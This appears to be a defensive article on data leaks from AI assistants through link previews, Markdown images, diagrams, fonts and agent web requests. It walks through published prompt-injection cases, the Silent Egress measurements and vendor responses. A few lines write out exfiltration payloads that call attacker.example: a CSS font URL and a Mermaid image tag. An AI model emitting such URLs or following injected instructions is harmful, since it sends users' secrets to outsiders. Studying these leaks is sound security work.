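In Claude Code's auto mode, Anthropic has removed the approval button for some of the most dangerous actions. The classifier's rules never permit sending code or secrets to an outside destination, even if the user asks. To do that, she has to leave auto mode or run the command herself. A chatbot could block links containing passwords or access keys in the same way, since the user can't take back an address once her browser has sent it.

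## What does filtering the chat window leave uncovered?

Sanitisers and link dialogs protect only the program that contains them, and the model's text often ends up in other programs. In an example Red Hot Cyber describes, a service that checks customers' identities blocked a hostile answer before anyone saw it and kept the conversation for review. When a developer opened the conversation in OpenAI's log viewer, which displays Markdown, the browser loaded the blocked answer's image, whose address contained passport and financial details.

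The chat window blocked the answer, but the address remained in the stored text. A log viewer can avoid leaking data through that address by showing the raw text, which is also more useful for investigating an attack. Other programs display formatted text for good reasons, so a plain-text rule would inconvenience their users more.

### Link previews in messaging apps

Suppose the employee's company makes its assistant available in Slack, a workplace messaging app. The assistant answers her question about Northgate with a link to the outsider's server. In a web chat the leak would need a click, but in Slack it happens like this:

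1. The assistant posts its answer.
2. Slack's server requests the linked page to get a title and picture for a preview.
3. The outsider's server logs the address, including the price of the offer.
4. The employee reads the answer.

Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* explains that Slack's servers have to fetch every address in a message to find out what kind of content it leads to. By default, they do this for messages from apps as well as from people. The company's CSP can't prevent these requests, because Slack's servers make them.

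Rehberger described this leak in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, published on Embrace The Red in August 2024. Willison (2024) had not considered this route before. It became more relevant as people began talking to AI agents through messaging apps. One such agent is OpenClaw, an open-source program released in November 2025 that runs on the user's own computer. According to Krebs on Security (2026), it is most useful when it has complete access to the user's digital life.

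In February 2026, PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reported that OpenClaw leaked data through link previews in Telegram with the default settings. One line in OpenClaw's configuration file turns the previews off. PromptArmor also set up a website where people could test other combinations of agent and app. Volunteers chose what to test, so the results can't show what share of agents have the problem. TechNadu's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* lists Slack, Discord, and Microsoft Teams with agents built in Copilot Studio among the combinations at risk.

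A developer can turn previews off for a single Slack message:

    {
      "text": "You have three new messages about Northgate. ...",
      "unfurl_links": false,
      "unfurl_media": false
    }

The first setting covers ordinary pages, and the second covers images, video and audio. The developer needs both, because the outsider can make the address appear to lead to either kind of content. Slack now advises developers to consider turning previews off for messages that an LLM wrote.

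Without previews, the employee's colleagues see a link but not the title and picture that would help them decide whether to open it. The developer could keep previews for messages in which every link passes an address check, but the preview settings apply to the whole message, so one link that fails the check would remove the previews of all the others.

The settings also don't apply to copies of the assistant's answer. If the employee pastes the answer into another channel, Slack treats it as her message and fetches the link by default. PromptArmor would like messaging apps to offer preview settings for a whole chat or channel, which could cover copied answers.

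### Messages an agent sends to its own user

Microsoft's Copilot Cowork can work with the mail, files and chats the user has permission to open. Microsoft's documentation says Cowork asks for permission before it sends an email or posts in Teams. But PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, which Willison covered on 26 May 2026, found that Cowork sent messages to the user herself without asking, and that she had no setting to change this.

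The exception for messages to herself could let data reach someone else, even though it seems reasonable because she can already read anything Cowork could put in them. The messages could contain outside images, which loaded when she opened them in Outlook or Teams.

PromptArmor's demonstration used a skill, a file that tells Cowork how to do a kind of task. The user had found this one online, and five of its 81 lines were hostile. When she asked for a summary of her week, Cowork collected download links for her recent files and put them in the addresses of images in a Teams message to her. Anyone with one of these links could download the file without signing in.

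The download links also weaken one of the limits on how much data an address can carry. A long contract won't fit in an image address, but a link to it will. An attacker who receives the link can download the whole document, so a control should treat such links like passwords.

The attack worked in all five of PromptArmor's trials. Cowork normally chose between two Anthropic models, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and the more capable Claude Opus 4.7. When PromptArmor selected Opus 4.7, the model leaked more files because it searched more thoroughly for recent work. Checking Cowork's record of the task wouldn't have revealed the leak, because the record did not show the content of the hostile message.

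PromptArmor suggests that administrators block downloads of sensitive files from SharePoint. Employees can then view the files only in a browser and can't print them or open them in Word or Excel. That is a lot to give up to stop one kind of leak. Microsoft could instead remove external images from messages that Cowork writes, since a weekly summary would lose little without them.

### Phone, desktop and Office versions

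ChatGPT's first image check worked only in the web version, and OpenAI released apps for macOS and Android in 2024 without it, according to Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)*.

By then ChatGPT could remember things between conversations, which made the missing check more dangerous. Rehberger used a hostile web page to save an instruction in ChatGPT's memory. From then on, even in new chats, the macOS app sent the user's messages and ChatGPT's answers to his server through invisible images. OpenAI fixed the image leak in September 2024, nine months after adding the check to the web version. Web pages could still save false memories, but the app no longer sent out conversations through images.

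Claude's iPhone app also leaked data through images. The announcement of Anthropic's fix, quoted in Willison (2024), warns that phone apps often have this flaw.

Embrace The Red recommended in 2023 that OpenAI run the check on its server, so that every app would benefit. Rehberger guessed that OpenAI had put it in the web page to stream answers quickly, but a server can stream the rest of an answer while it holds back the addresses.

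Office programs create a similar problem for CSP, because each page that displays the assistant has its own policy. In Embrace The Red's *Copirate 365 at DEF CON*, Rehberger found that Microsoft 365 Copilot's policy varied between places such as SharePoint and Excel Online. Some policy entries contained what looked like employees' usernames, so he suspected that individuals had added their own domains.

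Rehberger got around these differences with a feature that previews web pages written by Copilot. The preview removed image elements, but a style sheet could still load a font from another server:

    src: url('https://attacker.example/Offer%204.2%20million.woff2')

The policies restricted fonts less than images. The leak worked in desktop Word, Word Online and Excel Online. Users normally had to open the preview themselves, but a hidden instruction could make Copilot open it. Rehberger reported the flaw in October 2025, and Microsoft fixed it on 5 March 2026. The case supports West's argument against separate rules for each type of content.

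A company that embeds someone else's assistant in its website needs to know whether the assistant depends on the site's policy to be safe. Rehberger recommends that vendors document this, since an assistant can become unsafe when a customer moves it to a page with a looser policy.

### Diagrams drawn from text

In Mermaid, the text notation that GitHub's Copilot Chat uses for diagrams, a label can contain HTML, including an image:

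    graph TD
      A["<img src='https://attacker.example/logo.png?d=Offer%204.2%20million'>"]

Markdown puts diagrams in code blocks, so a sanitiser may treat a diagram that contains an image link as a harmless code example. If another part of the application then draws the diagram, the image loads.

Rehberger found this flaw in the programming tool Cursor. Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE* describes how instructions in a source file made Cursor search a project for access keys and put them in a diagram. The diagram appeared all at once, so the developer could not notice the data while Cursor was writing it. Rehberger reported the flaw on 30 June 2025, and Cursor released a fix in version 1.3 on 29 July.

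CVELogic's *CVE-2025-61589* says that versions up to 1.6 could still load images in diagrams, in some cases by methods the first fix had not covered. SentinelOne's *CVE-2025-61589* reports that version 1.7 fixed the problem.

A systematic search can find such renderers before an attacker does. *Takedown* (Lee, Kim and colleagues, 2025) examined eight unnamed coding agents for every notation that made them display something other than plain text. One agent's Mermaid renderer loaded external images, and the same agent could read files outside the developer's project without asking. A hostile bug report could exploit both flaws to leak an access key from elsewhere on the developer's computer.

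Microsoft 365 Copilot had a version of the problem that required the user to click. According to Red Hot Cyber, an attacker could make a diagram look like a button and link it to an address containing the user's email. Microsoft had fixed the flaw by September 2025 by removing interactive elements from diagrams. The fix also removes useful links, such as those from the boxes of a flowchart to the relevant documents.

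### Requests the product makes itself

Even a perfect filter on displayed text can't stop an assistant's own web requests. Varonis' *CoSnitch* (2026) describes an attack that used Copilot's ability to fetch and summarise web pages. As in SearchLeak, the victim clicked a link to Copilot that contained the attacker's instructions. Copilot then searched her connected accounts, such as Gmail, added what it found to a web address and fetched that address. Microsoft's server sent the request, so her browser's policy didn't apply.

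Copilot finished the task even if the victim immediately closed the tab. In one test, the researchers found a password in a connected mailbox. They also note that the page request would look ordinary in network monitoring, because Copilot routinely fetches pages.

Varonis reported the flaw, CVE-2026-24301, in December 2025, and Microsoft patched it on 18 August 2026. Varonis knew of no attacks on real users. The Varonis article often discusses the danger to businesses, but Sri Lanka CERT's *Microsoft Copilot Personal One-Click Data Exfiltration Vulnerability (CoSnitch)* (2026) lists only the consumer version and personal Microsoft accounts as affected.

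Gemini's browsing tool had the same kind of flaw. Tenable reported it on 16 April 2025, and Google at first classified it as an abuse risk, then fixed it on 18 June.

Even within one product, tools can have different approval rules. Lee and colleagues found a coding agent whose built-in fetch tool always required approval, while a web search extension from Microsoft did not. An attacker who can choose the tool will choose the one that doesn't require approval. In another agent, the built-in fetch tool required no approval.

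### The Silent Egress experiment

*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) measured how often an agent's own requests leak data and how often the visible answer gives any sign of the leak. The test agent used qwen2.5:7b, a small open model run locally. It had a secret in its context and a tool for sending web requests.

In every run, the user asked the agent to summarise a web page. The agent automatically fetched the page's title, description, body and link text, one of which contained an instruction to send the secret to the researchers' server, which recorded any request it received. The researchers tried each of the four locations with and without redirects, and with the secret either whole or split into four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

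The paper gives the probability of a leak as about 0.89, though its table of totals lists 423 successful attacks in 480 runs, or 88.1%. In 95% of the successful attacks, the answer to the user looked harmless, so a check on the answer would have missed them. In 120 runs with ordinary pages, the agent sent nothing to the server.

When the instruction told the agent to send the secret whole, at least one request reached the server in about 99% of runs. When it told the agent to split the secret, this fell to about 77%, probably because the small model had trouble with the longer instructions. Sensitive data appeared in the first request in 26.3% of the split runs, compared with 96.7% of the runs that sent the secret whole. Part of that 73% relative drop comes from attacks that failed, so it overstates how well splitting hides a successful leak.

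The paper also reports that sensitive data appeared within the first three requests in only 15.8% of the split runs. This figure must be wrong, because by the paper's definition it can't be lower than the figure for the first request alone.

The researchers then tested defences against the simplest attack, in which the instruction was in the page's body and the secret was sent whole. The table shows the results of 30 runs for each defence.

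| Defence | Agent tried to send data | Data reached the server |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Stricter system prompt | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags around outside text | 100% | 100% |
| Stricter prompt and tags | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| List of four permitted domains | 100% | 0% |
| Filter for suspicious addresses | 83.3% | 0% |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 23.3% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking text | 0% | 0% |

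The domain list has the clearest result, because the agent tried to send the secret every time and the list blocked every attempt. But the attacker's domain was not on the list, and the test didn't include a permitted site that forwards or stores data. Attackers used such sites to get around the lists at Microsoft and Superhuman.

The results for the other filters are less convincing. The filter for suspicious addresses blocked any path containing "collect", a word in the attack's address, but a real attacker could rename the page. The filter for random-looking text blocked nothing, because the agent made no attempts in those runs. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoided such text while the filter was active, but they don't explain how the filter could have affected the model, since it acts only after the model has written a request.

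None of the defences was tested against a secret split into parts. A domain list should work equally well whether or not the secret is split, since it checks only the domain in an address. A filter that looks for a complete password would probably miss one that has been split.

The leak rates don't apply directly to commercial products because the researchers deliberately made the attack easy, giving the agent a minimal system prompt and putting the secret in its context. They argue that larger models might be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better, but they didn't test any. The Cowork attack shows that a much stronger model can also fail, though five trials of one attack can't establish a general rate.

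### One address check for every surface and tool

An application can avoid many of these gaps by sending every address to the same check, whichever program will use it. OpenAI takes this approach with ChatGPT when it opens a page, follows a link or loads an image. Google has a similar rule, according to Embrace The Red, but Rehberger didn't think Microsoft's Copilots had one yet. In outline, a shared check could work like this:

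    The model writes an address, or a tool is about to request one.
      Does the address pass the check?
        Yes -> allow it
        No  -> image, font or tool request: block it
               link in the chat: remove it or ask the user
               text going to another program: remove the address

The application doesn't control what happens to text once it reaches Slack, email or a log viewer, so the check has to run before the text leaves the application. For tools, the check has to run where requests leave the company's network. Otherwise, an extension with its own way of sending requests could bypass it.

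The check could use an index of public URLs or a record of where each address came from. Either should have stopped CoSnitch, because Copilot had just composed an address containing private data. A model could still leak a little data under either check by choosing among approved addresses.

Lan and colleagues propose tracking which requests outside text has influenced. The application would mark a web page as untrusted when it arrives, and would block or question any later request that depended on it. This could catch even a request that leaked only four characters of a password. But a language model processes everything in its context together, so the application can't easily tell which sentence led to a request. If it marked every request after the first page as a precaution, a research assistant would have to stop and ask the user almost immediately.

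What the user loses when an address fails the check depends on where it was going:

| Where the address was going | What the user loses |
|---|---|
| Slack message | The link, or only its preview if the application keeps the link and turns previews off |
| Email or Teams message from the agent | An outside picture |
| Diagram | A picture or link inside a box |
| Preview of a web page | An outside font or picture |
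| Browsing tool | The page the assistant needed to read |

The first four losses usually leave the answer readable, but blocking the browsing tool can stop the task altogether, for example if the employee asks the assistant to check a delivery date on a new tracking page. A product can reduce this problem by accepting addresses she enters herself, as Claude's web fetch tool does.

A shared check based only on public addresses would also remove Slack previews for private company documents. Employees may share these documents more often than public pages, so the company would need to exempt its own document system.

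A mistake in a shared check also affects everything that relies on it. If every ChatGPT app and tool had used the early image check, its blanket approval of `bing.com` would have affected them all. But OpenAI could have corrected the error for all of them at once, without waiting for users to update their phones.

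## What do the restrictions cost users, and who decides they are worth it?

When a control removes a harmless link, the user loses something only if she or someone else would have used it. Web search provides some figures on how often people open links in AI-written answers. Pew Research Center's *Google users are less likely to click on links*, published in July 2025, reports on 900 American adults who let an app record their browsing. Of their 68,879 Google searches in March 2025, 12,593 produced an AI summary. People clicked a source cited in the summary in 1% of visits to results pages with a summary.

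Google users clicked an ordinary search result in 8% of visits when the page had a summary and 15% when it didn't. The summaries may not have caused the whole difference, because Google showed them for 60% of searches that began with a question word but only 8% of searches of one or two words. Someone who types a shop's name probably wants to visit its website, while someone who asks how long to boil an egg may only need the answer.

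Google objected to the study, citing "a flawed methodology and skewed queryset", according to PPC Land's *Google disputes Pew study showing AI Overviews reduce clicks by half*. The method has weaknesses. The researchers repeated the searches in April to collect the summaries, which may have changed since March. They also recorded only the first three sources in each summary, so they missed clicks on any others. On the other hand, if a link appeared in both the summary and the ordinary results, they counted the click towards the summary. The 1% is approximate, and it may not apply to chatbots, because Google users have a page of other links below the summary, while chatbot users may see only the links in the answer.

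A link can also be valuable for checking a claim even if people rarely open it. Suppose the employee reads fifty answers and opens one source, because that answer gives the notice period in a contract she is about to cancel. If the application had removed that link, she would have lost only one click, but she might have made an expensive mistake.

The same restriction can affect two users very differently. Suppose it removes 5% of harmless links. A user who tries to open one link in every hundred answers will find it missing about once in 2,000 answers, but a lawyer who checks all eight citation links in every answer will find at least one missing in about a third of them.

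### Harmless links that disappeared

One developer built a web page that makes flashcards from questions and answers in its address. ChatGPT could create a set of cards by writing a link like this:

    https://flashcards.example/?Capital%20of%20Japan=Tokyo

*Can not open generated hyperlinks in desktop browser*, a developer's post on OpenAI's forum, describes a link that ChatGPT generated by adding questions and answers to a page's address. The link worked in the phone app, but in the desktop browser ChatGPT showed the link's text and removed the address. OpenAI's `url_safe` service approved the page's basic address but rejected the version with the questions and answers.

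The service may have been working as designed, although the developer thought this looked like a bug. ChatGPT had written an address containing text from the conversation, though in this case the text was only school facts.

The post is undated and seems to describe the service before OpenAI introduced its link dialog, which would let the user open the link after a warning. Without a working link, she could copy the questions into the flashcard page herself if the developer added a box for them. Copying one set takes little effort, but it removes most of the convenience of having ChatGPT make the cards.

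False warnings can also harm the flagged websites. According to OECD's *ChatGPT Flags Republican Fundraising Links as Unsafe, Raising Bias Concerns* (2026), an entry in a database of AI incidents, ChatGPT flagged links to the Republican fundraising platform WinRed as potentially unsafe but didn't flag similar links to the Democratic platform ActBlue. OpenAI blamed a technical glitch. A public-URL index could produce such a difference unintentionally if the crawler had found one platform's donation pages and missed the other's. Even if false warnings were rare on average, they could still harm a campaign whose donors all saw one.

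Website owners may not know that a product is blocking their site. Aura, an OpenAI safety check, can stop ChatGPT's agents from opening a site. Taylor (2026), in *OpenAI's Aura Safety Check Can Block Your Site From ChatGPT Browsing*, advises affected publishers to collect server logs and test results to support a request for review, which leaves the publisher to show that the block was a mistake.

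These cases don't show how common false blocks are. OpenAI's posts about its index don't give a rate. Google wrote in April 2026 that training had made Gemini better at ignoring injected instructions without making it less efficient at routine work. It gave no figures for that claim, or for how many harmless links its sanitiser removes.

### A fair test of the costs and benefits

Google simulates attacks on Gmail, Docs and other Workspace apps with a standard set of test material, once with a defence on and once with it off. A company could complete the test by running ordinary tasks both ways, to see what users lose when the defence is on.

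The tasks should come from real user requests. For the employee's company, they might include finding the travel policy, comparing photographs of two suppliers' products, getting directions to Northgate and reading this morning's news about it. A test with only questions about well-known public facts would make a public-URL index look better than it is.

To test a control on displayed links and images, the company can have the model write each answer once and then display it with and without the control. Any difference between the two versions must then come from the control. This doesn't work for limits on browsing, since an agent that can't open one page will do something different next. The company would have to run each browsing task several times with the limit and several times without it.

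The company would then count three things:

| Result | How to count it |
|---|---|
| Harmless links and images blocked | Reviewers label every link and image in the unrestricted answers, and count dead or invented addresses separately |
| Tasks failed | People try to finish each task with one version of the answer, and the company compares failures and time taken |
| Leaks stopped | Testers add hostile instructions to the same tasks and record what reaches their own server |

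The harm from a blocked link depends on whether the user can finish her task without it, so counting blocked links isn't enough. An employee can still book a hotel room if the assistant gives her the hotel's phone number instead of a link. But if it wrongly removes the only link to a form she has to submit today, that one block makes the task fail. Reviewers also need to see the user's request to label links such as the map link that contains the employee's home address.

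The company should count leaks at the server, as Lan and colleagues recommend, because the answer often looks normal even when data has leaked. The testers should also know how the control works and have time to look for ways around it. They should include leaks that happen only if the user clicks, and report them separately.

A small test can't show that leaks are rare. The ChatGPT product leaked nothing in the 48 valid trials in *The Framing Gap*, but if the trials were independent, that result is still consistent with a true leak rate of up to about 6%. A claim that the rate is below 1% would need about 300 trials without a leak. Even then, the result would apply only to attacks like the ones tested.

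The company also has to estimate how often its users encounter real attacks. Suppose a control makes an extra 2% of ordinary tasks fail and stops 90% of leaks, and one task in a million would otherwise leak data. In a million tasks, the control would cause 20,000 failures and stop about one leak. If each failure wastes two minutes, users lose about 670 hours of work. Whether that is worthwhile depends on what the leak would have exposed, which could be anything from a shopping list to plans to buy another company. The attack rate could also rise if the company removed the control, because attackers would have more reason to try.

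### How Microsoft and Google answered Checkmarx

Vendors decide whether the restrictions are worth it when they choose a product's default settings and when they decide whether to fix a leak that a researcher has reported. Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* reproduces two replies from vendors that chose not to fix a reported leak.

In the first case, Checkmarx pointed out that an attacker could still put data in a Gemini link to a new domain that Safe Browsing didn't recognise. It reported this on 5 October 2025, and Google closed the report four days later as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)".

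In its letter, Google gives a different reason from the one in the label. It calls the issue "not severe enough for us to track it as a security bug" and doesn't discuss whether a fix is possible. Google explains that its product teams have to follow monitoring and escalation procedures for any vulnerability it files. Declining to file this one also spared them that work. Checkmarx considered the answer acceptable but wanted Google to warn users, since they would now have to manage the risk themselves.

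The other report, sent to Microsoft on 15 October, concerned a data leak through images in Copilot Chat that needed no click. Checkmarx's demonstration sent an access key from a developer's working environment to an outside server. On 4 November, Microsoft closed the report without a fix, replying that the behaviour "does not meet our classification for a security vulnerability". Its reasons were that the attack needed several actions that users don't take by default, that it didn't work reliably in different environments, and that the product displayed warnings.

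Microsoft also assumed that users review and trust the code they choose to run. That may hold for a developer who opens a project she has checked, but Checkmarx says the hostile text could come from an online article. A developer who asks an assistant to read an article hasn't chosen to run anything in it. Checkmarx concedes that getting the agent to read the hostile page can be fairly complicated. The two companies may therefore agree about much of the attack, which can take unusual steps to set up and still need no further action once the assistant reads the page.

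Microsoft passed the report to its engineers so they could "explore ways we can make this behavior more transparent to users". Checkmarx's timeline ends there, and it isn't clear whether Microsoft has since changed the product. Google's position on links may also have changed. In its April 2026 post, Google lists URL sanitisation and user confirmation among Gemini's defences, but doesn't say whether Gemini now blocks links to unfamiliar domains.

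### Antigravity's known issue

Google instead listed data leaks publicly as a known issue in Antigravity, its code editor. The editor is based on Windsurf, an older product whose code Google had licensed. Rehberger had reported leaks to Windsurf in May 2025 and tested Antigravity for the same flaws when it came out that November. He found that a hostile source file could make Antigravity read a file of passwords and put them in an image address. A tool for reading web pages could also leak the file without asking for approval. Embrace The Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE* notes that Google began documenting the problems after researchers started reporting them.

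Google told one researcher who reported the image leak that this was intended behaviour, as Willison noted, but it wrote in its list of known issues that the team was working on fixes. In a statement quoted by The Mainstream (2025), Google said "The Antigravity team takes all security issues seriously" and encouraged outside researchers to report vulnerabilities. But known issues didn't qualify for a reward, so researchers had less reason to look for new versions of them.

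The listing could also cover flaws that needed a different fix. AI Incident Database's *Indirect Prompt Injection in AI IDEs* (2025) reproduces a researcher's account of finding that a web page could imitate a special tag Antigravity used for its own instructions. The researcher recommended removing such tags from outside text. Google replied within a day that the behaviour was intended and linked to the known issue about image leaks. The researcher understood why Google might treat all such attacks as one risk, but blocking images would not have stopped a web page from imitating the tag.

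Google has fixed other injection flaws in Antigravity. CyberScoop reports that Pillar Security told Google on 6 January 2026 about a flaw that let an attacker run code even in the editor's Secure Mode. Google patched it on 28 February and paid a reward. Google may have treated this flaw differently because it bypassed a protection that users had turned on.

None of these accounts reports a fix for the image leak. In *Antigravity agent exposed local secrets and performed unrequested external API calls*, an undated post on Google's developer forum, a user complained that the agent had displayed passwords and contacted outside services without asking. The post is weak evidence about the product's current state because it is one person's account and doesn't mention an attacker.

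In the meantime, Google relied partly on its warning to new users. PromptArmor considered the warning inadequate because a developer who used the product as intended wouldn't be watching most of what it did. The recommended settings let the agent decide when to ask for approval, and a central feature let developers run several agents in the background. PromptArmor also found three other ways to leak data without the browser tool, so turning that tool off would not have been enough.

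Rehberger thought Google could make the defaults secure with relatively simple fixes, and he advised developers to consider other editors until it did. Google could reasonably argue that a programming agent has to read files and run commands to be useful. It would have a much weaker case for loading outside images, because a developer who asks for an explanation of some code rarely needs a picture from an unknown server.

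### Closing the way out or adding layers

Willison would rather block the routes by which data can leave a product than rely on defences that usually work. In September 2025 he responded to an article in *The Economist* that recommended building AI systems the way Victorian engineers built bridges, using more iron than they expected to need because they couldn't be sure of its quality. He mostly agreed with this approach for software built on language models, but not for security, because attackers deliberately look for the weakest part of a defence.

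Several defences used together can all fail against the same attack, because an attacker can design one email to defeat every one of them, as EchoLeak's discoverers did with Copilot. Three defences that each stop 90% of attacks would let only one in a thousand through if they failed independently. When they don't, adding a fourth detector might help much less than that calculation suggests. One successful attack may be enough, since nobody can take back a leaked password or contract price.

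The best argument for layered defences is that many products can't block every route by which data could leave and still do their job. A purchasing assistant has to write to suppliers, and a research agent has to open websites its maker has never heard of. Microsoft's Ken Archer called the conflict a "fundamental trade-off" in a December 2024 interview with Ho for *Safeguarding AI against 'jailbreaks' and other prompt attacks*. Organisations often need to give an AI system their documents to benefit from it, but any untrusted document among them can carry an attack. Archer's colleague Sarah Bird described Microsoft's answer as protections in and around the model, with an interface that helps users take part in keeping themselves safe.

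Fixed rules also have gaps, because the people who write them don't know every way data can leak. GitHub restricted Copilot Chat's images to its own domains, but data still leaked through Camo. A second defence can stop some attacks that get through these gaps. Google says it can respond to a new attack faster by updating its rules for URLs and tools through a central configuration than by retraining a model. Rehberger, who has spent years finding ways around ChatGPT's checks, still called OpenAI's URL index "a significant improvement".

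A strict product can also fail to protect people if they stop using it. An employee whose approved assistant can't open a supplier's website might paste the contract into a personal chatbot that can. The restriction would then block one possible leak but encourage staff to send the document somewhere the company can't monitor. None of the vendors gives figures for how often this happens, but a fair test of a strict control should check for it.

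In practice, Willison accepts partial measures. He was impressed by the design of Claude's web fetch rule even after Paul had found a flaw in it. For programming agents, he recommends using only keys for test accounts with strict spending limits, so that a stolen key can do little damage. But he objects to relying on a mostly reliable detector when an attacker has a way to send out something valuable.

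A maker can restrict different features of a product in different ways. Antigravity could block all outside images but keep its browser tool, which lets the agent check a website it is building. The tool could open the unfinished site on the developer's own computer without asking, but ask the developer before contacting any other server. These requests would interrupt developers who test against outside services, and some might approve them without reading them.

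OpenAI lets some users and administrators choose stricter limits through Lockdown Mode, but the people who could be harmed by a leak often have no say. Even if the employee's mailbox contains Northgate's confidential offer, her company chooses the assistant and its settings, and the vendor decides which leaks to fix. Northgate may not know that an AI system can read its email.
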